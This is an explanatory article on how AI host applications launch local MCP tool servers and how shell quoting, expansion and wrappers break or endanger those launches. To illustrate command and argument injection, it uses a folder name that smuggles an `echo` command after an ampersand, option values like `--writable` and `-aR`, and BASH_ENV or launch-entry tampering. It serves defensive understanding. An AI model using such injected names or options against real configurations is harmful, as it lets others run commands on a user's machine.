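# Command injection and quoting hazards when AI agents launch tool servers

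## How does an AI agent start a local tool server?

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open protocol through which AI applications connect to programs that offer tools and data. Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, introduced it in November 2024. AI agents depend on it heavily. An agent is a language model that works through a task by calling tools and reading the results: it might search a folder, then query a database. In announcing the specification of 28 July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) put downloads of the four main software kits at close to half a billion a month. (Downloads are not people, and an automated build can download the same kit many times a day.)

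Every connection involves two programs, a host application and a tool server. The host application is the AI application the person is using, such as a code editor or an agent platform. The tool server is a program that offers tools to a model over the Model Context Protocol (MCP). It can run on a machine in a data centre, but the protocol's *Architecture* (2026) also allows for local processes, so it can be a small program on the same laptop as the editor. The specification calls the component inside the host application that handles the connection to one server the client. Because the client is part of the host, the host application has to meet any requirements the specification sets for a client at launch.

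A remote server is already running, so the host application needs only its web address, but a local server has to be started. With the stdio transport, the host launches the server as a child process and exchanges messages with it over standard input and standard output, the two text channels that a program ordinarily has from the moment it starts. Under the Model Context Protocol's *stdio* specification, each message takes up one line, the server writes only valid messages to its output, and log text goes to a separate error channel.

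### The launch entry

The host application takes its instructions from a launch entry, the part of a configuration that gives a local server's command, arguments, environment variables and working directory. Take an imaginary tool server called notes-server, which lets a model search and read the text files in one folder. Its user, Ana, keeps her files in a folder named "R&D notes". Her entry looks like this:

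```json
{
  "servers": {
    "notes": {
      "type": "stdio",
      "command": "/usr/local/bin/notes-server",
      "args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"],
      "env": { "NOTES_LOG": "info" },
      "cwd": "/home/ana"
    }
  }
}
```

The layout follows the *MCP configuration reference* for VS Code, Microsoft's code editor. The name "notes" is just a label. The `type` field selects the stdio transport. `command` identifies the program to start, either by its full path, as here, or by a bare name that the computer looks up in the list of folders called the system path. `args` holds the arguments, the pieces of text passed to the program when it starts. Ana's entry has only one, the folder to open. `env` sets environment variables, named values that the program can look up while it runs. The variable in Ana's entry controls how much notes-server writes to its log, and many real entries use `env`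 to supply an access key. `cwd` is the working directory, the folder from which the program resolves any incomplete path. If Ana left it out and had a project open, VS Code would use the project's folder.

Other host applications have their own layouts. *MCP Config Examples*, from the coding assistant maker Tabnine, puts the same four fields under the heading `mcpServers`. VS Code also accepts a portable file at the root of a project, whose format has no field for a working directory. An entry that works in one host may need changes to work in another.

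In many published entries, `command` names a program that starts the server instead of the server itself. The Model Context Protocol's official beginners' guide, *connect local servers*, sets up a file server with `npx`, a package runner that fetches a package and runs it in one step. The arguments are `-y`, which confirms the installation automatically, then the package's name, then the folders that the server may open. Someone who reads only the `command` field therefore can't tell which package will run.

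### From entry to running program

When Ana opens her editor, the host application reads the file and decodes the JSON. Decoding removes the quotation marks, which only mark where each string begins and ends in the file, so they don't protect the ampersand in "R&D notes" in later steps. VS Code also fills in placeholders at this stage, such as `${workspaceFolder}` for the project's location. The host now has the path of a program, a list of strings, some environment variables and a folder.

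Next the operating system creates a process. On Linux the decisive step is a system call named `execve`. According to the Linux Programmer's Manual's *EXECVE(2)*, it passes the new program an array of strings as its arguments and a second array for the environment. By convention the first string in the argument array is the program's own filename. So notes-server receives this:

```
argv[0]   /usr/local/bin/notes-server
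argv[1]   /home/ana/R&D notes
```

Linux passes the folder's name to the program as one argument, without interpreting spaces or symbols such as the ampersand. Starting a program this way, from its path and an argument array with no shell in between, is called direct invocation. macOS works the same way. Windows passes the arguments as a single line of text, which causes other problems.

At this point notes-server is running, although the host application has not yet sent it any protocol messages. It can read and write files and open network connections with Ana's permissions. The beginners' guide warns that such a server can perform any file operation that the user could perform by hand.

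MCP itself begins only at this point. Until the revision of November 2025, every connection opened with a handshake called `initialize`, in which the two sides agreed on a version. The Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) records its removal. Under the specification of 28 July 2026, every request states its protocol version and what the client supports, so the host's first message can be a request to use a tool. The host may instead begin with `server/discover`, which every server must be able to answer but no host has to send. The reply lists the server's protocol versions and capabilities, and usually its name. The Model Context Protocol's *Discovery* (2026) states that the server reports this name, the protocol does not verify it, and clients should not rely on it for security decisions.

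So the host application can't tell whether a program is a tool server until it has run it. Suppose Ana's entry named `date`, the ordinary utility that prints the time. The host would have no sign that something was wrong until `date` had printed the time and exited. A host that supports old and new servers could still misread that sign. It sends `server/discover` first, and the Model Context Protocol's *Versioning and Compatibility* (2026) instructs it to treat anything other than a recognised modern reply as evidence of an older server, even though a program that doesn't implement MCP would produce the same evidence.

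The program may also run more than once. The stdio rules recommend that the host restart a server that exits unexpectedly. The Model Context Protocol's *Protocol versions* also describes an optional "auto" mode in the official TypeScript kit, which starts the program once as a throwaway probe and again for the real connection. The probe is useful because some older servers quit when they receive an unfamiliar first message. But the kit treats any program that exits during the probe as an older server, so `date` would run twice before the connection failed. By contrast, the Python edition of *Protocol versions* describes a host that fixes the protocol version in advance. That host sends nothing on connecting, so it has no reply by which to judge the program.

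This gap existed before the handshake was dropped. In the November 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol, the client also launched the server as a subprocess, and only then exchanged `initialize` messages over its input and output. An opening message can't vet a program before it starts, because the program must be running to receive it.

Any check meant to prevent harm therefore has to come before the launch. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* requires such a check in one case, when a host application lets people add a local server with one click. The host must first show the exact command, including all arguments and without truncation, and get the user's explicit approval. The user may still not be able to judge whether the command is safe, particularly when it contains `npx` and an unfamiliar package name.

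### A list of arguments and a line of text

So far no shell has appeared. A shell is a program, such as sh or bash on Linux and macOS or cmd.exe on Windows, that reads text as a command language and runs the result. Most people meet one in a terminal window. Ana might open a terminal and type:

```
notes-server /home/ana/R&D notes
```

This looks like the same launch as before to her, but the shell receives one string of characters and must use rules to work out where the folder's name starts and stops. Under the international standard for Unix-like systems (The Open Group, 2024), the shell first breaks the text into words and operators, then groups them into commands, performs expansion (replacing variables and file patterns with their values), handles any redirection of input and output, and finally runs the result. An unquoted space ends a word, and an unquoted ampersand ends a command,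 which the shell runs in the background while it continues with the rest of the line.

Ana's line therefore becomes two commands. The first starts notes-server on `/home/ana/R`, a folder that doesn't exist. The second tries to run a program called `D` with `notes` as its argument, and on most computers the shell prints an error because it can't find that program.

The standard lists the characters that a writer must quote if they are to stand for themselves, and both the space and the ampersand are on the list. Single quotes deal with both:

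```
notes-server '/home/ana/R&D notes'
```

Now the shell removes the quotes and passes the folder's name to notes-server as one argument, just as direct invocation did. Having to quote is reasonable for a person at a keyboard, since typing a line is easier than writing out a list. But a host application's launch entry already holds the arguments as separate strings. If the application joins them into a line and has a shell split it again, it must quote every string correctly, and it gains little unless the entry depends on expansion.

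Programming languages offer both routes, often side by side. MITRE's *CWE-78*, an entry in a widely used public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives the example of C, where `system()` accepts a single string containing the whole command, while `execve()` requires an array with one string per argument. The two calls treat Ana's folder very differently, though the choice between them can look like a matter of taste.

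### Three ways a launch can go wrong

Command injection happens when a shell reads data as part of a command and so runs something unintended. For example, a host application might build the command that starts notes-server by inserting the name of a shared folder without quoting it, then pass the command to a shell. If a colleague renames the folder `R&echo notes`, the shell starts notes-server on a folder called `R`, then runs `echo notes`, which prints the word "notes". This does no damage, but it means the colleague can run a command on someone else's computer by renaming a folder.

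Ana's own folder broke at the same character. In both cases, the shell read an ampersand in a name as an operator. The text after it happened not to name a program in "R&D notes", but it did in `R&echo notes`. An innocent quoting error and command injection share this mechanism and differ in who controls the text. A complaint that a server won't start when its folder name contains an ampersand is therefore a report of a security hole if strangers can influence that name.

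In argument injection, a program reads a piece of data as one of its own options. This can happen without any mistake by a shell, even when the program receives its arguments exactly as the host sent them. Suppose notes-server treats notes as read-only unless it receives the option `--writable`, and opens the working directory if no argument names a folder. A host application lets a visitor type the folder's name and passes it to notes-server by direct invocation. If the visitor types `--writable`, notes-server reads it as the option and gives the model write access to everything in the working directory, `/home/ana`.

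MITRE's entry on this weakness, *CWE-88*, describes a similar case. A program lists a file with `ls -l` and restricts the filename to letters, digits, underscores and hyphens, none of which has a special meaning to a shell. Someone supplies `-aR` as the filename and gets a listing of the entire directory and everything beneath it. MITRE recommends argument arrays against argument injection and rates their effectiveness as high. Arrays stop a value that contains a space from becoming two arguments, but they would not help here, because `-aR` is already a single argument and `ls` would still treat it as an option.

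An attacker controls the launch command if they can choose the program or the arguments in a launch entry. If someone can edit Ana's configuration and replace `/usr/local/bin/notes-server` with `date`, her host application will run `date`. This doesn't require a misread character or notes-server parsing data as an option, since notes-server never starts. If the entry uses a package runner, the attacker can leave `command` unchanged and change only the package name.

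MITRE's CWE-78 also covers this case, as a second subtype of command injection in which outside input selects the whole program, although MITRE describes the two subtypes as distinct programmer errors. A vulnerability notice labeled CWE-78 may concern either subtype, so you can't tell from the label alone whether better quoting would have helped. MITRE also notes that an attacker may be unable to chain several commands together when the application starts programs directly. But one program of the attacker's choosing is usually enough, and direct invocation will pass its arguments correctly.

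## Where does a shell enter the launch?

Two of MCP's official software kits, the libraries that a host application can use to start tool servers and talk to them, use no shell on Linux or macOS. Security reports, though, often describe an MCP launch as text going into a shell. In CSO Online's *RCE by design*, for instance, researchers at the security company OX Security object to user-supplied strings that "flow directly into a shell execution environment". The ampersand in "R&D notes" would break any launch that worked that way.

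### The launch code in the official kits

With the Python kit, a host application fills in a `StdioServerParameters` object, whose `command` is one string and whose `args` is a list of strings. In the Model Context Protocol's published source code, the function `stdio_client` works out which executable the command refers to, then passes it and the list as separate values to a helper that creates the process. Its documentation mentions only one forbidden character, the null byte, which marks the end of a string for the operating system.

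In case a shell runs later, the kit skips any variable whose value begins with `()` when it copies environment variables from the host application. Bash uses this form to pass on functions, and a comment in the code calls such functions a security risk. The kit doesn't apply this check to variables in the launch entry's `env` field.

The TypeScript kit takes the same two fields, and Model Context Protocol's *client/stdio* describes `command` as the executable to run. Cantina, another security company, reproduced the launch code in a threat advisory. Without its minor options, the call looks like this:

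```ts
spawn(command, args, { env, cwd, shell: false })
```

The setting `shell: false` makes Node.js start the server directly. The MCP TypeScript SDK's automated test *cross-spawn.test.ts* checks that the launch call receives the command, the argument array and this setting.

On Linux and macOS, both kits use direct invocation, so "shell execution environment" is the wrong description. OX Security's main complaint still holds. The malicious example in OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* puts a program's name in `command` and its arguments in a list, which works without a shell. An attacker who can set those values controls the launch command, and quoting can't prevent that. Adding quotes would even break Ana's launch, because with no shell to remove them, notes-server would look for a folder whose name contains quotation marks.

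The protocol's guidance may have added to the confusion. Cantina quotes an example from *Security Best Practices* in which a malicious startup command joins `npx` to a second program with `&&`. If a host application passed those pieces through either kit on Linux, `npx` would receive `&&` as an ordinary argument. The second program would start only if something other than the kit ran the command in a shell.

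On Windows, a tool server can be launched through a shell even when the caller sets `shell: false`. Model Context Protocol's *Releases* records that version 1.8.0 of the TypeScript kit added cross-spawn, a library that replaces Node's `spawn`. On Windows, cross-spawn checks whether the command leads to a file ending in `.exe` or `.com`. If it doesn't, the library escapes the command and arguments, joins them into one line and passes that line to cmd.exe. The kit's test can't catch this because it replaces cross-spawn with a dummy and starts no process. Setting `shell: true` would be worse, because cross-spawn then skips its escaping.

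The kit's developers previously left Node's shell option on. A maintainer said in *Make SDK work on Windows without additional arguments* (JonasHelming, 2024) that they removed it because it opened unnecessary terminal windows. Nobody in the thread mentioned command injection. After the removal, `npx` launches failed for some Windows users, one of whom patched the shell option back into a private copy. Cross-spawn eventually fixed the problem.

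The official C# kit is an exception. On Windows it has wrapped commands in `cmd.exe /c`, which caused the bug adner reported in *MCP - StdioClientTransport doesn't handle ampersands*. One argument was a web address with an ampersand before `connectionName`. The shell cut the address at the ampersand and gave an error that `connectionName` was not a recognised command, just as Ana's shell had tried to run `D`.

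### Six ways in

The most visible route is an entry that names a shell as its program:

```json
{ "command": "sh", "args": ["-c", "notes-server '/home/ana/R&D notes'"] }
```

The host application still uses direct invocation, but the program it invokes is `sh`, which reads the string after `-c` as a command. Bash works the same way, and the Windows equivalent is `cmd` with `/c`. Splitting the string into separate arguments doesn't make this as safe as invoking the server directly with an argument array. `sh -c` treats only the first string as the command, so passing `"notes-server"` and the folder as separate strings would start notes-server without its folder. `cmd /c` still reads the pieces as one line of text.

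A shell can also come from the host application's code, in which case the launch entry gives no hint of it:

```json
{ "command": "notes-server", "args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"] }
```

If the host calls Node's `spawn` with `shell: true`, Node joins these strings with spaces, without quoting them, and passes the resulting line to a shell. Ana's correct entry then fails the same way her unquoted terminal command did. Python's equivalent, `shell=True`, handles a list differently on Linux and macOS. The shell runs the first string as the command and doesn't pass the other strings to that command, so notes-server again starts without a folder.

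A security fix in Node.js stopped programs from starting Windows batch files directly, so before releasing version 1.92 of VS Code, its team told extension developers to set `shell: true`, either on every platform or only on Windows. Setting it on every platform also brings a shell into launches on Linux and macOS, where the batch-file problem doesn't exist. The coding agent opencode moved to cross-spawn for ordinary launches in March 2026. According to Hona in *fix(windows): use cross-spawn for shim-backed commands* (2026), `shell: true` had hidden the failures on Windows but caused problems with quoting and process management.

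The Python kit has its own shell option in `mcp dev`, a command that opens a testing tool for server developers. Ecosyste.ms' *GitHub / modelcontextprotocol/python-sdk issues and pull requests* listed a proposal to remove `shell=True` from the command's Windows launch as still open in April 2026. The option doesn't affect `stdio_client`, which host applications use.

Some package runners accept a whole command as the value of an option:

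```json
{ "command": "npx", "args": ["-c", "notes-server '/home/ana/R&D notes'"] }
```

Here `npx` passes the string after `-c` to a shell. Checking only `command` would reveal a familiar package runner but miss the shell. Bridge programs, which connect a local server to clients that use a different transport, can also invoke a shell. Yarn's *mcp-proxy* documents one with a `--shell` option and includes the option in its quick-start example.

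On Windows a familiar name may belong to a batch file, a script that only cmd.exe can run:

```json
{ "command": "npx", "args": ["-y", "notes-server", "C:\\Users\\Ana\\R&D notes"] }
```

On Windows, the `npx` in this entry is usually the batch file `npx.cmd`, so an entry copied from a Mac can launch through a shell even though `command` is unchanged.

Remote login adds a shell on another machine:

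```json
{ "command": "ssh", "args": ["ana-desktop", "notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"] }
```

The local computer passes all three arguments intact to `ssh`, the standard remote login program. But `ssh` joins everything after the machine's name into one line, which a shell on `ana-desktop` reads, so Ana would need a second set of quotes inside the last string. If the other machine runs Windows, cmd.exe may read the line instead, and Arch Linux's *Net::OpenSSH::ShellQuoter::MSCmd* warns that some servers require two kinds of quoting, applied in the right order.

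A container, a packaged program that runs with its own set of files, can also start through a shell:

```json
{ "command": "docker", "args": ["run", "-i", "notes-image"] }
```

Whether a shell runs inside the container depends on the form of the start command in `notes-image`. Docker, which runs the container, executes a command written as a list directly but passes one written as a plain line of text to `sh` inside the container. Ana can't tell from her entry which form the image uses.

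A client can split an argument without using a shell. In *MCP client violates shell words by joining commands and args with spaces*, a developer reported that an August 2025 version of Cursor, an AI code editor, had turned one argument into four. The log also shows that the argument `~/say.log` arrived unchanged. A Unix shell would have replaced the `~` with the user's home folder, so Cursor was probably splitting the text at spaces itself. Splitting this way would still give Ana two arguments, `/home/ana/R&D` and `notes`, but it wouldn't run a program called `D`.

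A May 2026 version of Cursor still had a related fault. In *MCP stdio command with spaces in path broken on Windows*, Cursor's staff confirmed that the editor split `command` at spaces whenever `args` was empty. Their workaround was to set `command` to `cmd` and move the path into `args` after `/c`. This avoids the faulty splitting but adds a real shell, which has its own rules for ampersands. *Can't use/escape spaces or use environment variables in MCP configurations* quotes another workaround from the makers of mcp-remote, a bridge to remote servers, which is to put a value containing spaces in an environment variable and refer to it by name in `args`.

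### Why people add a shell

People add a shell because they have a command that works in a terminal and want the host application to do the same thing. Often that command begins by changing directory. In October 2025 a user whose Shopify tool server wouldn't start in Cursor tried to run a local copy instead. According to *Shopify dev MCP not working on Cursor*, the new entry had `cd` in the `command` field and spread the rest across `args`: the project's folder, `&&`, `npx` and the package's name. Cursor's log joined the pieces into a line that would have worked in a terminal:

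```
cd /home/djordje/code/shopify-mcp && npx shopify-dev-mcp
```

The next log entry was `spawn cd ENOENT`. ENOENT is the operating system's code for "no such file or directory", and the missing file was `cd`, not the project's folder. `cd` is built into the shell, and most Linux systems have no separate program of that name. A separate program would not have helped, because it would have received `&&` and `npx` as arguments, and its change of directory would have ended when it exited.

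Wrapping the line in `sh -c` would have removed the error, but changing directory doesn't require a shell. Both kits accept a working directory as a separate value, so in a host application that exposes the field, Ana can write:

```json
{ "command": "notes-server", "args": ["."], "cwd": "/home/ana/R&D notes" }
```

The dot means the current folder, and nothing interprets the ampersand as an operator. Clearing the package runner's cache fixed the Shopify user's original fault, so the user did not need a different folder anyway.

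A similar error, `spawn uvx ENOENT`, has a different cause. According to the troubleshooting guide from dbt, which makes software for preparing data, a desktop application such as Claude Desktop may start with a limited environment and fail to find `uvx` on its search path. A terminal usually finds the program because its shell has read startup files that add folders to the path. Version managers, which let a developer keep several versions of Node.js or Python, often rely on the same files.

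This is why some people write `bash -lc` in a launch entry. The `l` makes bash behave as a login shell and read the user's startup files before it runs the command. dbt recommends putting the program's full path in `command` instead, for example `/opt/homebrew/bin/uvx`. This is safer but can be less convenient with a version manager, because the path may change at the next upgrade. The full path may also be insufficient for `npx`, a script that has to find Node.js on the search path. Setting `PATH` in the entry's `env` field can solve that without a shell.

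Chaining commands is harder to replace. Someone may want to activate a Python environment or fetch an access key before the server starts, but a launch entry can name only one program. That program can be a small script that runs those steps and then starts the server. A shell may still interpret the script, but the commands are in a fixed file and the script can receive the folder's name as a separate argument. The script must quote that argument when passing it on.

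Startup files can also break the protocol. Zed, a code editor, launches tool servers through the user's shell, and Docs.rs' *shell builder.rs* shows that the shell was interactive by default, the mode meant for a person at a keyboard. In that mode, many people's startup files print a greeting or a status message on the channel reserved for protocol messages. *Stop spawning ACP/MCP servers with interactive shells* reports that external agents hung on "Loading…" as a result, and switches the shell to non-interactive mode for both agents and tool servers. This reduces the stray output, but Zed still launches both through a shell.

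The table shows how many times a program splits or interprets the launch text after the host application has decoded the JSON. The counts are for Linux and macOS unless a row mentions Windows.

| Launch style | Times parsed | What parses the text |
|---|---:|---|
| Direct invocation | 0 | Nothing |
| Direct invocation of an `.exe` on Windows | 1 | The started program, which splits its line into arguments |
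| Host application that joins the strings and splits them at spaces | 1 | The host application |
| Entry that names `sh -c` or `bash -lc` | 1 | The named shell |
| Host application with Node's shell option on | 1 | `sh` |
| `npx -c` with a command string | 1 | The shell that `npx` starts |
| `cmd /c` with an `.exe` on Windows | 2 | cmd.exe, then the started program |
| `npx` as a batch file on Windows, through cross-spawn | 3 | cmd.exe on the opening line, cmd.exe again inside the batch file, then Node.js |
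| `ssh` to a Linux or macOS machine | 1 | The login shell on that machine |
| `sh -c` with an `ssh` command inside it | 2 | The local `sh`, then the remote login shell |
| Container whose start command is a plain line | 1 | `sh` inside the container, which reads the image's start command |

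## How do quoting and expansion break a launch on Linux and macOS?

A shell processes a launch command in stages, and different stages give special meaning to different characters. It can misinterpret an ampersand in a folder name at the start and a dollar sign in a password later. Adding quotation marks until the error message goes away is therefore unreliable, because marks that protect the folder name may not protect the password.

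### The order in which a shell works

The standard from The Open Group, known as POSIX, fixes the order. Once the shell has split the line into tokens (words and operators) and grouped them into commands, it processes the words:

1. It replaces a leading `~` with the path of a home folder, a variable such as `$HOME` with its value, and a command substitution such as `$(date)` with the output of the command inside. It also works out any arithmetic written as `$((...))`.
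2. It splits the results of unquoted replacements into separate words, normally at spaces, tabs and line breaks.
3. It treats unquoted `*`, `?` and `[` as file patterns and replaces each pattern with the names of matching files.
4. It removes the quotation marks and backslashes that did the quoting.

Bash has an extra step, brace expansion, which the Bash Reference Manual's *Shell Expansions* puts first. It turns `{draft,final}` into two words.

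Because the shell looks for operators before it fills in variables, an ampersand inside a variable's value can't end a command. Suppose a variable called `FOLDER` holds `/home/ana/R&D notes`. These are the argument arrays that result, with the program's name first:

```
notes-server $FOLDER      ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D", "notes"]
notes-server "$FOLDER"    ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
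```

The unquoted version gives notes-server the wrong folder, but the shell never looks for a program called `D`, and a colleague could not run `echo` by renaming the folder `R&echo notes`. Argument injection is still possible. An unquoted value of `/home/ana --writable` becomes two arguments, and the second gives the model write access. An unquoted `*` becomes a list of the files in the working directory, so a file named `--writable` would have the same effect.

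Quotation marks stored in a variable don't keep its value together, because the shell removes only those in the original command. If Ana stores `'/home/ana/R&D notes'` in `FOLDER`, including the quotes, and then writes `$FOLDER`, notes-server receives two arguments, `'/home/ana/R&D` and `notes'`.

### A folder, a password and a tilde

Ana's folder has a harder time when its name is part of the command text itself:

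```json
{ "command": "sh", "args": ["-c", "notes-server /home/ana/R&D notes"] }
```

The shell processes the string like this:

```
tokens         notes-server | /home/ana/R | & | D | notes
first command  notes-server /home/ana/R    (in the background)
second command D notes
expansion      nothing to replace, split or match
first array    ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R"]
second array   ["D", "notes"]              (program not found)
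```

This launch would fail even if Ana had a folder called `R`. Under POSIX, a non-interactive shell connects a background command's standard input to `/dev/null`, which is empty. So notes-server would reach the end of its input at once and never receive the host application's messages. Model Context Protocol's stdio rules recommend that a server exit when its input ends.

The shell, meanwhile, can't find `D` and exits with status 127, the standard code for a missing command. From the host's side, a program started and then quit. The Shopify user's `ENOENT` error, by contrast, meant that the operating system couldn't start anything. A 127 in a host's log is a good hint that a shell was involved.

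Either kind of quotation mark fixes the folder. In the launch entry the two versions of the command string are `"notes-server \"/home/ana/R&D notes\""` and `"notes-server '/home/ana/R&D notes'"`. The arrays are the same as with direct invocation:

```
double quotes      ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
single quotes      ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
direct invocation  ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
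```

The two kinds of quotes treat some other characters differently. Suppose notes-server also accepts a password as an argument, Ana's password is `blue$ky7`, and she'd like to write her folder as `~/R&D notes`. (An argument is a poor place for a password, since other users of the same computer can often read it.) The table shows what notes-server receives in each case.

| Launch | `/home/ana/R&D notes` | `blue$ky7` | `~/R&D notes` |
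|---|---|---|---|
| `sh -c`, no quotes | `/home/ana/R` | `blue` | `/home/ana/R` |
| `sh -c`, double quotes | Unchanged | `blue` | Unchanged, with a literal `~` |
| `sh -c`, single quotes | Unchanged | Unchanged | Unchanged, with a literal `~` |
| Direct invocation | Unchanged | Unchanged | Unchanged, with a literal `~` |

Inside double quotes, the dollar sign, backquote and backslash keep their special meanings. The shell therefore treats `$ky7` in Ana's password as a variable, finds none by that name and replaces it with nothing. Ana then sees a wrong-password error that doesn't mention that the shell shortened her password. A password containing `$$` would be even more confusing, because the shell replaces those two characters with its own process number, so the password would usually be different at each launch.

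Single quotes preserve every character, but they can't contain a single quote. For the password `ana's$key`, Ana would have to write `'ana'\''s$key'`, which closes the quotes, adds an escaped single quote and reopens the quotes.

Both kinds of quotes stop the shell from replacing the tilde, so quoting all of `~/R&D notes` to protect the ampersand breaks the reference to Ana's home folder. She can leave the tilde and slash outside the quotes, as in `~/'R&D notes'`, or write `"$HOME/R&D notes"`. The tilde must also come at the start of the word, so `sh` would not replace the one in `--folder=~/notes`.

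When a host application invokes notes-server directly, no shell expands the tilde. Unless notes-server expands it itself, it looks for a folder named `~`. Model Context Protocol's *Debugging* recommends absolute paths because a host application may start a server from an unpredictable folder, such as `/` on macOS, which makes relative paths like `./data` unreliable.

### JSON, the host application and the shell

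Before a shell reads any of this, the host application has already decoded the JSON and may have filled in variables of its own.

JSON uses the double quote to end a string and the backslash to escape characters, so Ana has to write `\"` to give the shell a double quote and `\\` to give it a backslash. If she wants the shell to read `"blue\$ky7"`, where the backslash protects the dollar sign, the file must contain `\"blue\\$ky7\"`. With only one backslash before the dollar sign, the file isn't valid JSON.

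JSON also allows `\u0026` for an ampersand, and some programs save files that way. This doesn't protect the ampersand from a shell, because the host decodes `R\u0026D` to `R&D` before it starts the server.

Anthropic documents two forms of variable substitution for its coding agent, Claude Code, `${VAR}` and `${VAR:-default}`. Both work in `command`, `args` and `env`, and in the `url` and `headers` of a remote server. Claude Code looks up the value in its own environment, so it won't find a variable that Ana defines only in the entry's `env` field. If a variable is unset and has no default, Claude Code issues a warning and leaves the text `${VAR}` in place.

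Whether anything parses the value again depends on what the entry starts. Claude Code is built on the official TypeScript kit, which uses direct invocation on Linux and macOS. If `NOTES_DIR` holds Ana's folder, this entry therefore gives notes-server a single argument, ampersand and space included:

```json
{ "command": "notes-server", "args": ["${NOTES_DIR}"] }
```

The company FutureSearch published a launch entry that uses the same method to put a database password into an argument for `uvx`. A dollar sign in that password would do no harm, because direct invocation bypasses the shell. But the receiving program still applies its own rules to the argument, which is a database address with the password between a colon and an `@`. A password containing `@` could therefore make the program parse the address incorrectly.

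Adding a shell to Ana's entry produces this sequence:

```
in the file         "notes-server \"${NOTES_DIR}\""
after JSON          notes-server "${NOTES_DIR}"
after Claude Code   notes-server "/home/ana/R&D notes"
after the shell     ["notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
```

The launch works only because of what this particular value contains. Claude Code inserts the folder's name before the shell starts, so the shell reads the name as if Ana had typed it in the command. If the value were `blue$ky7`, the shell would cut it to `blue`. A value containing a double quote could end the quoted part early and add another command.

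It is much safer to let the shell fill in the variable, which Ana can do by writing `"$NOTES_DIR"` without braces, since that isn't one of the two forms that Claude Code replaces. The shell inserts the value after it looks for operators, and the double quotes prevent it from splitting the value. She should also set `NOTES_DIR` in the entry's `env` field, because a local server inherits only a limited set of variables.

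The two layers also handle some shared syntax differently. If `NOTES_DIR` exists but is empty, a POSIX shell expands `${NOTES_DIR:-/home/ana}` to the default, `/home/ana`, while Claude Code counts the variable as set and inserts an empty string. The folder that notes-server receives can therefore depend on which program expands the text first.

Anthropic has blocked one case in which substituted values reached a shell. A remote server's entry can include `headersHelper`, a command that generates login details, and Claude Code runs it in a shell. Before version 2.1.207, Claude Code inserted a plugin's user settings into that command. It now reports an error instead. In its documentation, Anthropic suggests putting the setting in `headers`, which "isn't shell-parsed", or having the helper read it from a file.

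There is one more layer if Ana adds the server by typing a command instead of editing the file:

```
claude mcp add --transport stdio notes -- notes-server '${NOTES_DIR}'
```

Claude Code passes on everything after the `--` unchanged, but the shell in Ana's terminal processes the whole line first. Because she uses single quotes, the configuration file stores the reference `${NOTES_DIR}`. With double quotes, the shell would replace the reference with its current value, and the file would store that instead. This matters little for a folder, but if the variable held a password, the file would store it in plain text.

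### Separate arguments after sh -c

Someone who knows that argument arrays are safer might try to combine one with a shell:

```json
{ "command": "sh", "args": ["-c", "notes-server", "/home/ana/R&D notes"] }
```

As before, the folder never reaches notes-server. According to the POSIX Programmer's Manual's *sh(1p)*, the shell puts the string after the command into a special variable, `$0`, and any further strings into `$1`, `$2` and so on. Ana's folder is therefore in `$0`, which GNU's *Invoking Bash* describes as the shell's name in warnings and error messages.

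This mistake can be worse than a crash. If the working directory is `/home/ana`, notes-server opens that directory instead, and the model can read text files across Ana's home folder.

The usual remedy is `"$@"`, which stands for all the arguments from `$1` onwards and keeps each one separate. But adding it to the command string isn't enough, because the folder is still in `$0` and `"$@"` is empty. The entry also needs a placeholder for the name:

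```json
{
  "command": "sh",
  "args": ["-c", "exec notes-server \"$@\"", "start-notes", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
}
```

Now `start-notes` goes into `$0` and the folder into `$1`. The `exec` matters for shutdown. The command string is fixed and doesn't contain the folder's name, so the shell can't treat any part of the name as an operator, even in a name like `R&echo notes`. Without the quotes around `$@`, the shell would split the folder's name at its space. `"$*"` is also wrong because it joins all the arguments into one.

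A script file avoids the placeholder:

```sh
#!/bin/sh
exec /usr/local/bin/notes-server "$@"
```

If Ana saves this as `/home/ana/bin/start-notes`, makes it executable and names it in `command`, the first string in `args` becomes `$1`. Any setup commands go on the lines before `exec`.

Neither version stops argument injection, since `"$@"` delivers `--writable` as faithfully as a folder's name.

### Stray output from the shell

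A wrapper that quotes everything correctly can still break the connection by printing a line such as "Welcome back, Ana" to standard output, among the protocol messages. Start-up files can print such a line, and which ones run depends on the shell and its options. The table combines GNU's rules for bash with those in Zsh's *Files* for zsh, the default shell on current Macs, and uses the files' standard locations.

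| Launch | Start-up files that run first |
|---|---|
| `sh -c` | None |
| `bash -c` | The file named in the variable `BASH_ENV`, if it is set |
| `bash -lc` | `/etc/profile`, then the first readable file among `~/.bash_profile`, `~/.bash_login` and `~/.profile` |
| `bash -ic` | `~/.bashrc` |
| `zsh -c` | `/etc/zshenv` and `~/.zshenv` |
| `zsh -lc` | The two `zshenv` files, then the system and personal `zprofile` and `zlogin` files |
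| bash on another machine, through `ssh` | Usually `~/.bashrc` |

The problem in the last row is easy to miss because Bash normally skips `~/.bashrc` when it runs a single command. But Bash does read the file when it detects that a remote login service started it, so a greeting there on `ana-desktop` could corrupt a launch that works when Ana runs it locally. Zsh reads `.zshenv` every time it starts, and Zsh's guidance is that the file shouldn't contain commands that produce output.

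`BASH_ENV` also affects security because bash runs whatever file the variable names. Someone who can edit only the `env` field of a bash entry can therefore still change what runs.

Commands inside the wrapper can print too. *Run MCP Server with a specific node version (NVM)*, from the testing company BrowserStack, gives a launch entry for the company's own server. The entry uses bash to load nvm, a version manager for Node.js, then runs `nvm use 22.16.0` and starts the server with `npx`. `nvm use` normally prints a line confirming the version. Writing `nvm use 22.16.0 >&2` sends that line to standard error, where MCP allows it. A redirect inside the command string can't do the same for output from start-up files, because the shell runs those files before it reads the string.

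Stray text made Zed hang, but other hosts may report errors instead. *MCP Server stdout pollution causing Invalid JSON-RPC messages in Claude Desktop* describes a user of Postman's tool server who got repeated "Invalid JSON-RPC message" errors at every startup. The cause was a library inside the server that printed its log messages to standard output, not a shell. GitHub's debugging guide also lists debug output from the server as a common cause of parse errors, so you can't tell from the error alone whether a wrapper is at fault. Running the same server directly, without the wrapper, would help to tell the two causes apart.

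A shell can also interfere with input. `sh -c` takes its commands from the string and leaves standard input for the server, but a start-up file that prompts for input could read the host's first message as the reply. An entry that names `sh` with no arguments would be dangerous, because the shell would read the host's MCP messages as commands.

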